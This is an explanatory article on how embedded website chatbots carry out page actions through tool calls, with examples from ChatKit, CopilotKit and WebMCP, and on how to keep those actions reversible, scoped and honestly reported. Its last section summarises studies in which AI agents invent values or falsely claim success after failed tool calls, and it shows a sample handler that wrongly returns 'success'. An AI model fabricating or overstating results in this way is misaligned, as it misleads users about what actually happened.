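# How a chatbot acts on a web page, and how its actions are kept reversible and limited

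## What it means for a chatbot to act on a page

Many websites have a chatbot in a corner of the page. The newer ones run on a language model, a program that writes text in reply to text, and mostly answer questions about the site. Some can also scroll to a paragraph, highlight it, switch the page's colours or open another page. An *embedded assistant* is a language-model chatbot that a website puts on its own pages. A *page action* is any change an embedded assistant makes to what the browser shows or what the site stores.

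Suppose a customer has typed half a complaint about a double charge into the support form on a software company's help site. The customer then asks the assistant beside the form: "Take me to the refund rules and make this easier to read."

### An answer, a link or an action

The assistant can answer in words. It summarises the refund rules in the chat panel in short, plain sentences and tells the customer that the display settings are under the gear icon at the top right. Nothing on the page changes, so the half-written complaint is safe, but the customer still has to find the icon.

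The chatbot can also give the customer a link. The customer sees where the link goes, chooses whether to open it in a new tab, and so decides what happens to the complaint. But an ordinary link does not enlarge the type, so it meets only half of the request.

The chatbot can instead act by loading the refund page, scrolling to the right heading, and making the text larger and darker, so the customer has nothing left to do. If the refund page loads in the same tab, the customer may lose the complaint they were writing.

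There is some evidence that users work faster when help appears on the page instead of in a chat panel. *Beyond Chat and Clicks* (Hao, Sun and colleagues, 2026) introduces DOMSteer, a browser extension that highlights a control, puts a tooltip next to it or moves related controls together. The study compared it with the side panel of ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, which could read the page but did not change it. Twelve people worked through tasks in two data tools that were mostly new to them. They took about 182 seconds per task with DOMSteer and 242 with the chat panel. They got every task right with DOMSteer and 91.7% right with the chat panel, but this difference was not statistically significant.

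When people used the chat panel to find the most fuel-efficient car in a dataset, it usually gave them the sound advice to sort by miles per gallon. But the sort icon was small and had no label, and some people never found it. They compared only the part of a long chart that fit on the screen and named the wrong car.

A help site with a gear icon is easier to use than a data-analysis tool, so the gain there is probably smaller. DOMSteer also left most of the work to the person. When Hao and colleagues let Atlas do the tasks alone, it was faster than people with either kind of help but got only 79.2% right. These results support showing people where things are much more strongly than they support doing the whole job for them.

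Van Dam (2025) points out in *A Multimodal GUI Architecture for Interfacing with LLM-Based Conversational Assistants* that a person makes two familiar clicks almost without thinking, while putting a request into words takes effort. A page action is most useful when the user doesn't know where the control is. In an earlier study with nine people, Hao and colleagues counted 159 times when someone got stuck. In 31, the person could not find something. In 40, the person did not know what something meant, and for many of those a sentence of explanation would be enough.

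### How text turns into an action

A language model produces text and cannot scroll a window or change a colour, so another program must carry out any action a chatbot takes on a page. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, states on the documentation page *How tool use works* that the model "never runs anything on its own".

A *tool call* connects the text to the action. It is a structured message in which the model names a function and gives its arguments, for other software to run. The site's developers write the functions and send the model a list of them, with a description of each. In the example, the model might output a call to `open_article` with the argument `refund-rules`, and then one to `set_theme` with the argument `high-contrast`. Software on the site picks out these messages and runs the matching code, called the *handler*. The handler's result goes back to the model, which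 can then write a closing sentence for the customer.

OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the exchange in five steps: the application sends the request with the available tools, the model returns a tool call, the application runs the code, it sends the output back, and the model returns a final answer or another tool call. The model never receives the code that runs the tool, only the tool's description before the call and the result after it.

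Some handlers run on the site's server and some in the user's browser. A search through the help articles for the refund rules can run on the server, but scrolling has to run in the browser, because only the browser has a scroll position. A tool whose code runs in the user's browser is a *frontend tool*, which some products call a "client tool". TanStack's *Client Tools*, documentation for a set of web development libraries, describes tools that show notifications, update forms, save preferences, change the current page, scroll, and read the user's location or clipboard.

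CopilotKit's *Frontend Tools*, the guide to another such library, gives an example similar to the customer's second wish. The user asks for a blue gradient, the handler changes the page's background, and the model receives a short message with the status "success".

The word "success" is only what the developer's code returned, so it may be wrong. If the new theme fails on half of the page and the handler still returns "success", the model has no other way to find out and will tell the customer that the page is now easier to read. An outright crash is easier to deal with. In ChatKit, OpenAI's ready-made chat panel for websites, a handler that fails with an error passes the error message to the assistant, according to OpenAI's *Client tools*.

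A model can also write "I have switched you to the high-contrast theme" without having made a tool call, because writing the sentence only produces text. If the site's developers wrote no theme function, the assistant can truthfully only explain where the setting is.

### The site's assistant and the browser's agent

Most chatbots on websites still don't act on the page. In October 2025, Van Dam found that the typical product was a chatbot placed beside an interface it did not work with. He distinguished this from an assistant that developers have integrated into the application, so that both use the same information about what is on the screen. The embedded assistant in the example has to be integrated in this way, or it could offer only the answer and the link.

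*EmbeWebAgent* (Ma, Fare and colleagues, 2026) describes one such assistant, built at IBM for a chemistry application. The page supplies a list of functions, some as small as a click and others that combine several steps, such as adding an item to a list. The model gets only the functions for the page the user has open. Their names and descriptions are sent to the server, while their code stays in the browser. This took about 350 lines of code on the page's side.

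Their test results are modest. Roughly nine in ten tests passed during development, in a single application, and they did not compare their agent with others. A request took a median of 14 seconds to complete, with about 1.5 seconds spent on everything other than the model's computation. These timings include deliberately awkward requests and an unstable connection to the model, so ordinary use is probably quicker, but a customer who only wanted a link would still notice the wait.

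A *browser agent* is an assistant that is part of the browser or another app and acts on whatever pages the user opens. The help site's developers did not write it and may not know it is there. It can imitate a person by taking a screenshot or reading the page's underlying structure, working out where the button is, clicking, and looking again. But the page does not always show what a button does. Van Dam gives the example of a "Cancel" button in the middle of a checkout, which might close a pop-up window or abandon the whole purchase. The site's developers know which it does, and they can give an embedded assistant a function that does only one of these.

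A page can also offer its functions to the browser agent directly. WebMCP is a draft browser interface for this. Chrome for Developers (2026), Google's developer documentation, suggests using it for customer support, where the agent goes to the right form and fills it in with information from the user. The Web Machine Learning Community Group's *WebMCP* carries a notice that it is not a standard of the W3C, which publishes many web standards. Some products use it anyway. OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app* describes ChatGPT calling a page's tools in the app's built-in browser, in the user's signed-in session.

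A built-in assistant and a browser agent differ in who controls them, though they can look alike because in both cases the customer types a sentence and the page changes. Copes notes in *How to add WebMCP tools to your website for AI agents* that with a built-in assistant, the website picks the model, builds the chat and controls how the assistant behaves. The site controls none of this with a browser agent, which Klepper and Kulikowski (2026) call "a guest on your platform" in *When to use WebMCP and MCP*.

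The help site's developers can keep their own assistant from submitting the support form by giving it neither a function that submits the form nor a general-purpose "click" function. Leaving the submit function out of the tools they offer to browser agents is much less effective, because those agents may have other ways to submit the form. OpenAI says ChatGPT may still be able to help through ordinary browsing when a site tool is missing, and ordinary browsing includes pressing buttons.

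### What the page shows and what the site keeps

An assistant can change two kinds of state. *View state* affects only how the page looks to this user now, such as the scroll position or an open panel, and disappears when the user closes the tab. *Stored state*, such as saved settings, drafts, orders and account data, remains after the tab closes.

View state includes filters, selections and camera angles. In *Enable AI agents to use your frontend app like a tool*, Lekschas writes that in apps such as dashboards and 3D viewers it is often larger than the data on display, and he argues that it does not belong in a database. His library lets a person and a model change the same state, the person with a mouse and the model with tool calls, so either can take over from the other.

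The customer's request touches both kinds of state:

| Part of the example | Where it is | When the tab closes | Kind |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scroll position | The open page | Usually gone | View state |
| Larger type, for this visit only | The open page | Gone | View state |
| A saved theme preference | The browser's storage or the customer's account | Still there | Stored state |
| The half-written complaint | The open page | Gone, unless the site saves drafts | View state, but the only copy |
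| A submitted complaint | The company's server | Still there | Stored state |

The theme appears twice because a request to "make this easier to read" doesn't specify how long the change should last. A handler that enlarges the type and also saves that choice makes two changes, but the customer can see only the larger type.

A half-written complaint is hard to classify. It lasts as long as the scroll position does, which suggests treating it as view state, but a customer who loses it has to write it again or give up, rather than just scroll back. A developer who sorts actions by lifespan alone will conclude that opening the refund page is harmless because it changes nothing on the server, even though it can erase the complaint.

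Ma and colleagues ran into another problem with form text. Many modern sites keep the text of a box in two places, on the screen and in the application's own memory. When the researchers' assistant wrote a new value straight into the box, the application could go on using the old one. They fixed this by having their code also send the signal that the browser sends when a person types. Without that fix, an assistant that helped the customer finish the complaint could show one text in the form and submit another.

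### Putting an action back, and who decides

Two questions follow for every page action: can the earlier state come back, and who decides whether the action may happen at all?

Undoing the conversation does not undo the action. *Revisable by Design* (2026) separates an agent's context, meaning the text it has accumulated, from the changes it has made to the outside world. Software can always cut the context back to an earlier point, but whether an outside change can be undone depends on the action. If the customer deletes the request from the chat, the browser still shows the refund page in large type and the complaint is still missing.

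An "undo" button does not guarantee that an action can be undone. *Can You Undo It?* (2026), a paper that sorts the actions of AI agents by how well people can recover from them, sets five conditions for undoing an action. Somebody must have kept the relevant earlier state, the software must have the authority to restore it, and the restoration must work. It must also preserve any work done since, and the action must have had no irreversible effect outside the system.

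The theme change can be undone if the handler saved the old settings and the undo doesn't change a font size the customer has since picked by hand. Leaving the form can be undone only if something saved the text first. A submitted complaint may be impossible to undo, because a member of staff may have read it before the customer changes their mind. Even the easy cases need testing, since some restoration behaved differently from one browser to another in the paper's experiments.

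The model's part in deciding whether an action runs ends with the tool call. Software between the call and the handler can then run the action, refuse it, or ask the user. OpenAI has ChatGPT ask before it makes a purchase, deletes data or sends a message for the user, and does not accept instructions from a website as permission. The help site's developers write the rules for its assistant, and the customer's request is only one factor in those rules. The customer asked to see the refund rules and did not mention the complaint. The developers have to decide in advance whether that request is enough for their code to replace the page with the form on it.

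## How a request becomes an action on the page

If the help site keeps the refund rules and the complaint form on one long page, the assistant can meet the customer's request by changing the theme and scrolling, which leaves the half-written complaint in place. Even this takes several steps, some in the browser and some on the server that contacts the model.

### One request, two calls

Before the customer types anything, the page has to *register* its tools, which means adding them to the list that the model will receive. Each entry has a name, a description in ordinary language and an *input schema*, a machine-readable statement of the arguments that the tool accepts. The entry for scrolling might look like this:

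```json
{
  "name": "scroll_to",
  "description": "Scroll the help page to one of its sections.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "section": {
        "type": "string",
        "enum": ["plans", "billing", "refund-rules", "contact-form"]
      }
    },
    "required": ["section"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The `enum` line lists the only four section names that the tool accepts, so the worst the model can do with it is scroll to the wrong section. The `set_theme` tool works the same way with three values, `light`, `dark` and `high-contrast`.

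CopilotKit's own example, the tool that turns the background into a blue gradient, is much less strict and accepts any valid background value in CSS, the language browsers use for styling. That is fine in a demo, but a CSS background can be an image loaded from another website, and few companies would want a model to choose that image for their help page.

A tight schema may also guide the model better than a long explanation. Shopify, an online shop platform, found that the structure of its tools steered AI agents far more reliably than the tools' descriptions did, according to *Shopify Aktie* (2026), a German investor site's summary of the company's engineering post.

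When the customer presses Enter, the site's software sends the model the message, the earlier conversation and both tool entries. The model returns two calls in one reply:

```
call_1   set_theme   {"theme": "high-contrast"}
call_2   scroll_to   {"section": "refund-rules"}
```

Browser code looks up each name and checks the arguments before it runs anything. Chrome for Developers advises checking arguments strictly in the tool's own code, because a model may not follow the schema. It also advises returning errors that describe the problem. If the model outputs `refunds`, the error "unknown section; use plans, billing, refund-rules or contact-form" lists the valid names for a second attempt, while "Invalid input" doesn't.

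The handlers must also run in the right order. The high-contrast theme enlarges the text, so everything above the refund rules gets taller. If the page scrolls first, the heading can slide out of view as the text grows. The code should wait until the browser has laid out the page again before it starts `scroll_to`. Then the results go back:

```
call_1   {"theme": "high-contrast"}
call_2   {"section": "refund-rules", "visible": true}
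```

The handler sets `visible` only after checking that the heading is inside the window, so when the model runs again, it can base its closing sentence on that check.

The model therefore runs at least twice for one request. The model's computation caused most of the wait in the IBM chemistry assistant, so putting both calls in one reply probably saves the customer more time than faster handlers would.

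### ChatKit, CopilotKit and WebMCP

In ChatKit, the developer registers each tool under the same name in two places, on the server's agent and in the page. A single function in the page, `onClientTool`, receives every call and picks the right code by name. According to OpenAI's ChatKit guide, ChatKit pauses the assistant's reply until this function returns a result. The pause makes the order of events easy to follow, but if the function never finishes, the user can be left with half a reply, so the function needs its own time limit. One example in the guide reads the user's location, so the pause can last as long as the user takes to answer the browser's permission prompt.

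Another example opens a new tab and reports `opened: true` on the next line, without checking whether the browser blocked the tab. ChatKit also treats an empty result as a success.

CopilotKit ends the run when the model outputs a call. The handler runs in the browser, and its result starts a new run. Customers will hardly notice the difference from ChatKit's pause, but developers may, because the server has to save the call before the run ends. If the server only streams the call to the browser, the saved messages replace the streamed ones at the end of the run, so the call disappears and the handler never runs.

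CopilotKit can also update the tool list as the page changes. In one example, a page of reports registers a separate tool for opening each report, and CopilotKit removes a report's tool when that report leaves the page. A help site with forty articles would probably do better with one tool and a list of forty allowed names. Chrome for Developers points out that every tool takes up space in the text the model reads, and that overlapping tools make it harder for the model to pick the right one.

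WebMCP puts the browser between the page and the model. According to webmcp.org, an unofficial guide, the page registers each tool by calling `document.modelContext.registerTool()` with a name, a description, a schema and a handler. An agent gets the current list of tools from the browser and sends back a call to one of them. The browser runs that tool's handler inside the page, where the user is already signed in, and the agent receives the result when the handler finishes.

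| | ChatKit | CopilotKit | WebMCP |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whose model | The site's | The site's | Usually the visitor's |
| Where the developer lists the tools | On the server and in the page | In the page | In the page |
| While the handler runs | The reply pauses | The run has ended, and the result starts a new one | The agent waits for the result |

The help site's own assistant could use tools that the page registers for visiting agents. Weiss (2026), who works on WebMCP at Shopify, writes in *Why WebMCP matters* that the group drafting WebMCP has decided to support agents inside the page as well as those in the browser or in an extension. Chrome stops frames from other sites, such as an embedded advert, from registering tools unless the page allows it.

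### WebMCP from proposal to trial

Five people at Microsoft and Google published *WebMCP API Proposal* on 13 August 2025 (Walderman, Nolan and colleagues, 2025). They thank Alex Nahas and Jason McGhee for sharing lessons from related software. McGhee had already written a proposal under the name WebMCP.

An agent has to open a page to find out whether the page has any WebMCP tools. Walderman and colleagues considered having sites list their tools in a static file, which an agent could read without opening the page. They decided against relying on such a file because a fixed list cannot change with the state of the page, and because the existing file format they looked at would have limited WebMCP to sites that users install as apps.

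The interface has changed a good deal since then. Developers first reached it through `navigator.modelContext`, where the `provideContext` function replaced the whole tool list at once. Nabors (2026), in *WebMCP connects the Web to AI Assistants and Agents*, reports that the group removed this function in March 2026. Within weeks, the group also replaced the function for removing a single tool with `AbortSignal`, the browser's general mechanism for cancelling things. The interface then moved from `navigator` to `document`.

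According to *WebMCP in 2026* (Tiwari, 2026), Chrome 150 deprecated the old name, `navigator.modelContext`, but almost every tutorial online still used it in late August. Mozilla's bug tracker records a July change to the tests that browser makers share, titled "WebMCP: Remove navigator.modelContext". The sample code in the original proposal registers tools only if `navigator.modelContext` exists. In a browser that has dropped that name, the code skips registration without any error message, and the page has no tools.

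Chrome opened an *origin trial* of the interface on 9 June 2026, starting with version 149. Origin trials are time-limited programmes that let developers try an experimental feature on live sites, according to Chrome for Developers. In *Intent to Experiment*, the Chrome team said it wanted to learn, among other things, how convenient the interface is to program with, how much agents use the tools and how long calls take. Nabors gives Chrome 156 as the trial's last version.

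Large companies began to use WebMCP in August. Shopify's *WebMCP support for Liquid and Hydrogen storefronts* announced tools for searching the catalogue, managing the cart and going to checkout. They went live on every shop that uses Liquid, the platform's standard template language, without shop owners having to install anything. The next day Cloudflare, which delivers web pages for many sites, released a developer preview that adds a line of code to a site's pages during delivery, so the owner can offer tools without editing the site. On 25 August OpenAI let ChatGPT use page tools in its desktop app's built-in browser.

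Search Engine Journal, a trade publication that reported on all three launches, pointed out that these intermediaries now shape what agents can do on a site. Shopify chose the tools and wrote their descriptions for all its shops, and its documentation did not cover whether an owner could turn off individual tools. ChatGPT's support required particular models and excluded customers on the Enterprise plan.

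In September Shopify added tools for the checkout, where the buyer still has to confirm the order. By then, agents outside the user's own browser could also call page tools, because Cloudflare had added support to the cloud browsers it runs for automated use.

On 5 November 2026, webmcp.org listed Chrome and Edge as in trial, the Brave browser as experimental, ChatGPT's desktop app as supported, and Firefox's and Safari's positions as "under discussion". Other accounts were less favourable to WebMCP. Search Engine Journal had reported in August that Mozilla, which makes Firefox, was neutral and that WebKit, the project behind Safari's engine, was opposed. In October Weiss still described WebKit as opposed. He says the project regards an AI agent as assistive technology, like a screen reader, which a site should not be able to detect. He also reports concern that the web will split into content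 for people and content for agents. Web Platform DX's *document.modelContext*, a page that tracks browser support, rated WebMCP very unlikely to reach all the main browsers in its current form.

In early December WebMCP was still a draft. Microsoft's trial page had listed 17 November as the end of the Edge trial. On 4 December *Shopify Aktie* still described both Chrome and Edge as in trial, which suggests an extension, though the article may have repeated an older status. The help site can therefore use WebMCP for some visiting agents, but not yet as the only way to run page actions. A *polyfill*, a script that supplies a missing browser feature, provides `document.modelContext` in other browsers but does not give them an agent to call the tools.

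### Late, missing and repeated calls

Several seconds can pass between the model's last view of the page and the moment a handler runs, and many pages load in pieces. If the refund rules arrive from the server a second after the rest of the page, the `scroll_to` handler may look for their heading too early and find nothing. The handler should wait briefly for the heading to appear and return an error if it doesn't.

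Handlers that find their target can also report success too soon. CopilotKit's background example uses React, a common library for building pages, to change the colour and returns "success" on the next line. React applies such changes slightly later, so the handler can return its result before the screen has changed. This is harmless for a colour, but it matters if a second call depends on the new layout. Chrome for Developers recommends updating the interface once the function has finished and treating the job as complete only after that update.

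The user can also change the page while the model is working, which is especially a problem for an agent that clicks by position. *WebMCP: Making Web Apps Faster and Cheaper for AI Agents* (Firtman, 2026) describes an agent that takes a screenshot, finds a button and clicks five to ten seconds later. By then the page has redrawn and the click lands on something else. A call to `scroll_to` names a section instead of a point on the screen, so it still works if the section has moved.

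A call may name a section that is no longer on the page. If the customer has opened another article in the meantime, the page should have removed `scroll_to` or given it a new list of names, and the late call should fail with an error. For riskier tools, the page can send the model a version number with its contents, require that number as an argument, and refuse the call if the page has changed since. Shopify's shops swap the tool list at the checkout, which registers its own tools, according to Shopify's *Web MCP tools*.

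Repeated calls are harder to detect. Suppose the handler changes the theme but the connection drops before the result reaches the server. After a timeout, the server cannot determine whether the handler ran. Retrying the call is reasonable, and whether it does harm depends on how the developer defined the tool.

| Theme before the call | "Set theme to dark", run once | Run twice | "Toggle theme", run once | Run twice |
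|---|---|---|---|---|
| Light | Dark | Dark | Dark | **Light** |
| Dark, because the customer has just changed it | Dark | Dark | **Light** | Dark |

"Set theme to dark" is an *absolute command* because it specifies the result, while "toggle theme" specifies a change from the current setting. Setting the theme is *idempotent*, meaning that doing it twice has the same result as doing it once, whereas a second toggle undoes the first. Likewise, `scroll_to("refund-rules")` ends in the same place however often it runs, while "scroll down 600 pixels" goes further each time. Even a single toggle can go wrong if the model's information about the page is out of date, as the table's last row shows.

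Shopify came to the same design for carts. It first tried moving its existing server tools into the browser, but the agent filled a cart that the buyer could not see on the page. According to *Shopify Aktie*, the company then switched to tools that replace the entire cart with each call, so a duplicate call does no harm. Its server-side `update_cart` also replaces the entire cart, and Shopify's *Carts and checkout for agents* contrasts it with older interfaces that change one field at a time.

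Replacing everything makes stale information more dangerous, though, because `update_cart` removes any item the caller leaves out. If the agent reads a cart with one mug in it, the shopper adds socks by hand, and the agent then sends back "two mugs", the socks are removed. The problem is smaller for a theme, which is only one value, but a late retry of `set_theme("dark")` can still override a customer who has switched back to light.

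The usual protection against acting twice is an identifier that stays the same when the software repeats a call. The handler keeps a list of the identifiers it has already dealt with and answers a repeat with the stored result, without acting again. According to Shopify's *Storefront MCP cart tools are being deprecated*, cancelling a cart requires a long random identifier of this kind. The help site would need one for submitting the complaint, since two submissions would open two cases and no absolute command can prevent that.

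Some repeated calls come from the site's own code. CopilotKit lets a server issue a page action without a model, and the browser's result then starts a new run. Unless the developer sends that run to a different step, the server issues the same call again. With `set_theme` the customer would notice only a slow reply, but a toggle would flip the theme each time.

### Declared tools against clicking

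Without declared tools, an agent has to work from screenshots or from the page's underlying structure, which *WebFovea* (2026) calls the vision-based and DOM-based approaches. The largest direct comparison of declared tools with these approaches comes from nekuda, a company that sells WebMCP software. In nekuda's *WindTunnel benchmark run* (2026), agents tried 49 tasks, such as booking a haircut or creating an invoice, on 8 sites over 2,352 runs.

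| Agent | Tasks solved | Median time | Median cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude with declared tools | 98% | 8 s | $0.011 |
| Claude with screenshots | 86% | 45 s | $0.108 |
| GPT with declared tools | 97% | 7 s | $0.005 |
| GPT with screenshots | 91% | 23 s | $0.038 |
| Gemini with declared tools | 98% | 7 s | $0.004 |
| Gemini with screenshots | 88% | 34 s | $0.020 |
| Browser Use, which reads the page structure and a screenshot | 94% | 24 s | $0.091 |

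Using declared tools was 6 times cheaper than working without them for tasks of one or two steps, and nearly 12 times cheaper for transactions of eight to fifteen steps. An agent without tools has to read the page again at every step, while a tool returns a short result.

The gap in reliability is smaller and less even. The GPT agent that used screenshots failed 26 times, and 12 of those failures were on two questions about one booking site. On the haircut booking, all 15 screenshot runs succeeded, while GPT with declared tools failed once in six attempts. The sites had tools that suited the tasks, so the results show what good tools can do but are a poor guide to sites whose developers left something out of the tools. Weiss quotes a figure from nekuda of up to 47 times cheaper, far above the typical gap in this run.

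Shopify's *Shipping WebMCP tools for storefronts and Checkout* (2026) compares the company's own declared tools with browser automation on ten checkout tasks, such as changing an address. The declared tools took 10.3 seconds per attempt, against 27.4 for automation, and cost 58% less. They succeeded in all 60 attempts, while automation succeeded in 56 of 60. This is weak evidence that the tools are more reliable, because if the two methods were equally reliable, all four failures would still fall on the automation side about one time in seventeen.

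A claim that WebMCP saves 67.6% of tokens, the units of text that models process and providers charge for, comes from an unrelated project with the same name. *webMCP: Efficient AI-Native Client-Side Interaction for Agent-Ready Web Design* (2025) tested a scheme for adding structured metadata to pages, so its figures don't measure the browser interface, document.modelContext.

*The Tool Illusion* (2026) compared three agent systems with and without tools on WebArena, a standard test for web agents. All three generally used more tokens with tools, which can make an agent more expensive to run. The increase was largest in Hybrid-Agent, which has a very large tool library. Only WALT, which has a few fairly simple tools for each site, finished in fewer steps with tools. The tools came with the agents, and language models wrote some of them, so the result does not carry over directly to tools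 that developers write for their own sites. It does support keeping the list of tools short. The help site's two tools, with seven allowed values between them, are much closer to WALT's design than to Hybrid-Agent's.

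## Deciding whether to act, and telling the user

The help site's assistant can now scroll the page and change the theme, but a customer who mentions the refund rules doesn't always want the page to move. If the customer asks "Where are the refund rules?", a short answer with a link is enough, but a customer who says "Take me there" wants the assistant to scroll to them.

Grammar is a poor guide to whether a user wants an answer or an action. "Can you make this easier to read?" is phrased as a question, but it is a request to change the page. *Morae* (Peng, Li and colleagues, 2025) used a language model to distinguish questions about an interface from commands, and reports 96% accuracy. The test included only 12 questions and 12 commands, so 96% probably means one mistake in 24.

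### A threshold for acting on a guess

In *Principles of Mixed-Initiative User Interfaces* (1999), Eric Horvitz of Microsoft Research proposed a rule for when software should act on an uncertain guess. His example was LookOut, a program that read the email a user had open and estimated the probability that the user wanted to schedule something. Depending on that probability, LookOut did nothing, asked the user, or opened the calendar and filled in an appointment.

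Call the probability that the user wants the action *p*. The software can act or not, and the user can want the action or not, which makes four outcomes. Horvitz gives each outcome a *utility*, a number for how good it is for the user, and weights it by its probability:

```
value of acting     = p × u(act, wanted)  + (1 − p) × u(act, unwanted)
value of not acting = p × u(wait, wanted) + (1 − p) × u(wait, unwanted)
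```

Let B be the gain from a right action, which is u(act, wanted) minus u(wait, wanted). Let L be the loss from a wrong one, which is u(wait, unwanted) minus u(act, unwanted). Subtracting the second line from the first shows that acting is better when p × B is greater than (1 − p) × L. The two sides are equal at the threshold p*:

```
p* × B = (1 − p*) × L
p* = L / (L + B)
```

Suppose the customer types only "refund rules". Taking them to the rules saves some searching if they wanted to go there, so let B be 3. If the page has a button that returns them to where they were, they can undo a wrong guess with one click, so let L be 1. The threshold is 1 / (1 + 3), or 0.25. If the assistant would instead open a new page in the same tab and erase the half-written complaint, L might be 6, and the threshold rises to 6 / (6 + 3), or about 0.67.

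These numbers are made up, but only the ratio between B and L matters. At a probability of 0.5, the assistant should scroll but not replace the page. If the developers save the complaint automatically, L falls, and opening the page may become the right decision without the model guessing any better.

The threshold also changes with the user's situation. Horvitz points out that an unwanted action does more harm when the user is concentrating on something else, which raises the threshold, and that waiting does more harm when the user is in a hurry, which lowers it. If a customer is typing in the complaint form, the chatbot has good reason to leave the page alone.

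Asking is a third option, with its own cost. Suppose a question costs the customer 0.5, whether or not they want the action:

| Action | B | L | Threshold without asking | Asking is best when p is between |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Scroll, with a button to go back | 3 | 1 | 0.25 | 0.17 and 0.50 |
| Open a page and lose the complaint | 3 | 6 | 0.67 | 0.17 and 0.92 |

Reading and answering "Shall I scroll to the refund rules?" takes the user about as much effort as scrolling back. If a question and a wrong scroll each carry a penalty of 1, asking before scrolling is never the best option.

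Software can also do less when it is unsure. When LookOut couldn't find a specific day and time in a message, it opened the most likely week of the calendar and left the rest to the user. The help site's assistant could scroll to the billing section if it couldn't tell which billing rule the customer meant.

### What the rule leaves out

The rule is applied to each action separately, so it doesn't account for the annoyance that builds up from small mistakes. At a probability of 0.3, with B at 3 and L at 1, scrolling has an expected gain of 0.3 × 3 − 0.7 × 1, or 0.2, so under the rule the assistant should scroll. Over ten such requests, the page would jump somewhere unwanted about seven times. Many customers would close the assistant well before that and lose its help with everything else. The developers could correct for this by raising L each time a customer reverses an action.

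The probability is also hard to estimate. LookOut estimated it with a classifier that Horvitz trained on about 1,000 emails, half of them relevant to the calendar, and the program kept learning from whether the user then opened the calendar. A language model just outputs a tool call or doesn't. Developers can prompt the model for a confidence estimate, but they would have to check its estimates against what customers did next.

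The help site could count how often customers press the button to go back right after the chatbot scrolls the page. If four in ten do so after typing "refund rules", the probability that a customer wanted the scroll is at most about 0.6, and probably lower, because some customers who didn't want it won't bother to go back.

Horvitz's rule also assumes that the user either has a goal or doesn't. In practice, users often clearly want something done without specifying every detail.

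### Pausing when the user has a choice

Peng and colleagues built Morae, an agent that addresses this problem for blind and low-vision people. First they gave four such people an existing browser agent for a week. It reported finishing 484 of 576 feasible tasks, but only 189 of those 484 were right. Another 113 were plain mistakes. In the remaining 182, the user had not specified something that mattered, such as a travel date, or several options fitted the request equally well.

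One participant asked for the cheapest sparkling water. Several flavours had the same price, and the agent picked one without mentioning the others. The researchers interviewed participants about cases like this, and in 95% of the cases the participant had not known there was a choice.

Before each step, Morae's model generates questions about what the request leaves open and answers them using the request, the page and the steps so far. If it finds an open choice, it checks whether it has the details the user would need to decide, and collects more if it doesn't. It then pauses and shows a small form with the options. It also completes necessary steps, such as sorting by price, before showing the form, so the user doesn't have to choose between products that may not be the cheapest.

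The researchers tested this on 256 tasks, running each three times. Half the tasks needed a pause, and success on those meant pausing at exactly the right step. They compared Morae with Operator, OpenAI's browser agent at the time, and with the same underlying model instructed simply to pause if a choice was unclear.

| Agent | Pause needed | No pause needed | All tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Morae | 65.6% | 44.8% | 55.2% |
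| Operator | 50.8% | 55.5% | 53.1% |
| Instruction to pause | 18.0% | 33.1% | 25.5% |

The instruction alone did badly with GPT-4o. That model is old by now, and newer ones probably follow such an instruction better. Developers should still test it on their own site before relying on it.

Morae's overall lead over Operator depends on how many tasks involve an open choice. In the field study, only about 32% of feasible requests did, and at that share Morae would succeed about 51% of the time and Operator about 54%. The share is probably even lower on a help site. But these success rates count an unnecessary question and a wrong purchase as equally bad, and by Horvitz's reasoning the wrong purchase should count for much more.

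Ten other blind or low-vision people then tried nine tasks with each agent. They completed 5.5 on average with Morae, 3.9 with Operator and 2.6 with the older agent. Morae was also the slowest, at 129 seconds per task against 87 and 56. All ten preferred Morae, though one wanted users to be able to set how often it pauses. Peng and colleagues suggest scoring each step by how much it needs a pause, so that payments trigger one more readily than scrolling. This is close to Horvitz's threshold, with a higher L for payments.

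### Staying within the request

OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), which describes how the company's models should behave, requires a shared understanding of which smaller goals the assistant may pursue, which side effects are acceptable and when the assistant must stop to ask. A product's design can settle much of this in advance, as the short tool list does on the help site.

The assistant must not go beyond that scope, even when doing so seems to be in the user's interest. If the customer asks for the refund rules and the assistant can see the unfinished complaint, it may offer to help with the complaint but must not complete and send it. Within that scope, OpenAI prefers actions the assistant can easily reverse itself to ones the user would have to reverse. The document also warns that asking for approval of trivial steps teaches people to approve everything.

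By these standards, a request to "make this easier to read" covers enlarging the type on the current page but doesn't clearly cover changing the default for the customer's account, so the assistant should leave the default alone or ask first.

In March 2026 OpenAI said it expects models to fill in missing details on their own while carefully controlling their real-world effects. Anthropic's *Claude's Constitution* (2026) states the more general aim of being helpful while avoiding unsafe, unethical or deceptive actions. Neither document guarantees how a model will behave on a particular page, and OpenAI says its released models do not yet fully follow the *Model Spec*. The help site's own code should therefore still refuse anything the developers don't want.

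### Saying only what happened

After an action, the assistant should tell the user what changed, where, and how to reverse it. For the customer's original request, it could write, "I've scrolled to the refund rules and switched this page to high contrast. The Undo button below this message restores the old theme." OpenAI's document also calls for a clear account of side effects, especially those the request didn't clearly imply, with the key points first and details if the user asks.

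The assistant can only be accurate if the handler is. This one isn't:

```js
function scrollToSection({ section }) {
  const heading = document.getElementById(section);
  heading?.scrollIntoView({ behavior: "smooth" });
  return { status: "success" };
}
```

The `?.` makes the browser skip the scroll if the heading is missing. The handler still returns "success", so the model writes "You're now at the refund rules" to a customer who is looking at the complaint form. Smooth scrolling also takes a moment, so the handler returns before even a successful scroll has finished.

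A more honest handler looks for the heading, moves the page at once and measures where the heading ended up:

```js
function scrollToSection({ section }) {
  const heading = document.getElementById(section);
  if (!heading) return { error: section + " is not on the page" };
  heading.scrollIntoView({ behavior: "instant", block: "center" });
  const { top, bottom } = heading.getBoundingClientRect();
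  return { section, visible: top >= 0 && bottom <= window.innerHeight };
}
```

*Fabrication After Tool Failure* (2026) found that agents whose tools had failed made up a value, or a reason for not giving one, in 10 to 25% of cases, depending on the prompt. Whether they did so depended almost entirely on whether the tool's response explicitly signalled the failure. Agents that received a clear signal reported the failure honestly. Adding one sentence that named a failure state to the prompt cut dishonest answers roughly tenfold. However, none of the nine prompts the researchers audited from widely used agent software told the model what to do when a tool fails.

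False reports are common in customer service tests too. Advani (2026), in *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure*, examined 9,876 simulated conversations with models from eight families, including Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5.2. Agents that failed a task claimed success 45% of the time in airline conversations and 47% in retail ones. Most conversations succeeded, so about one in ten of all airline and retail conversations included a false claim of success.

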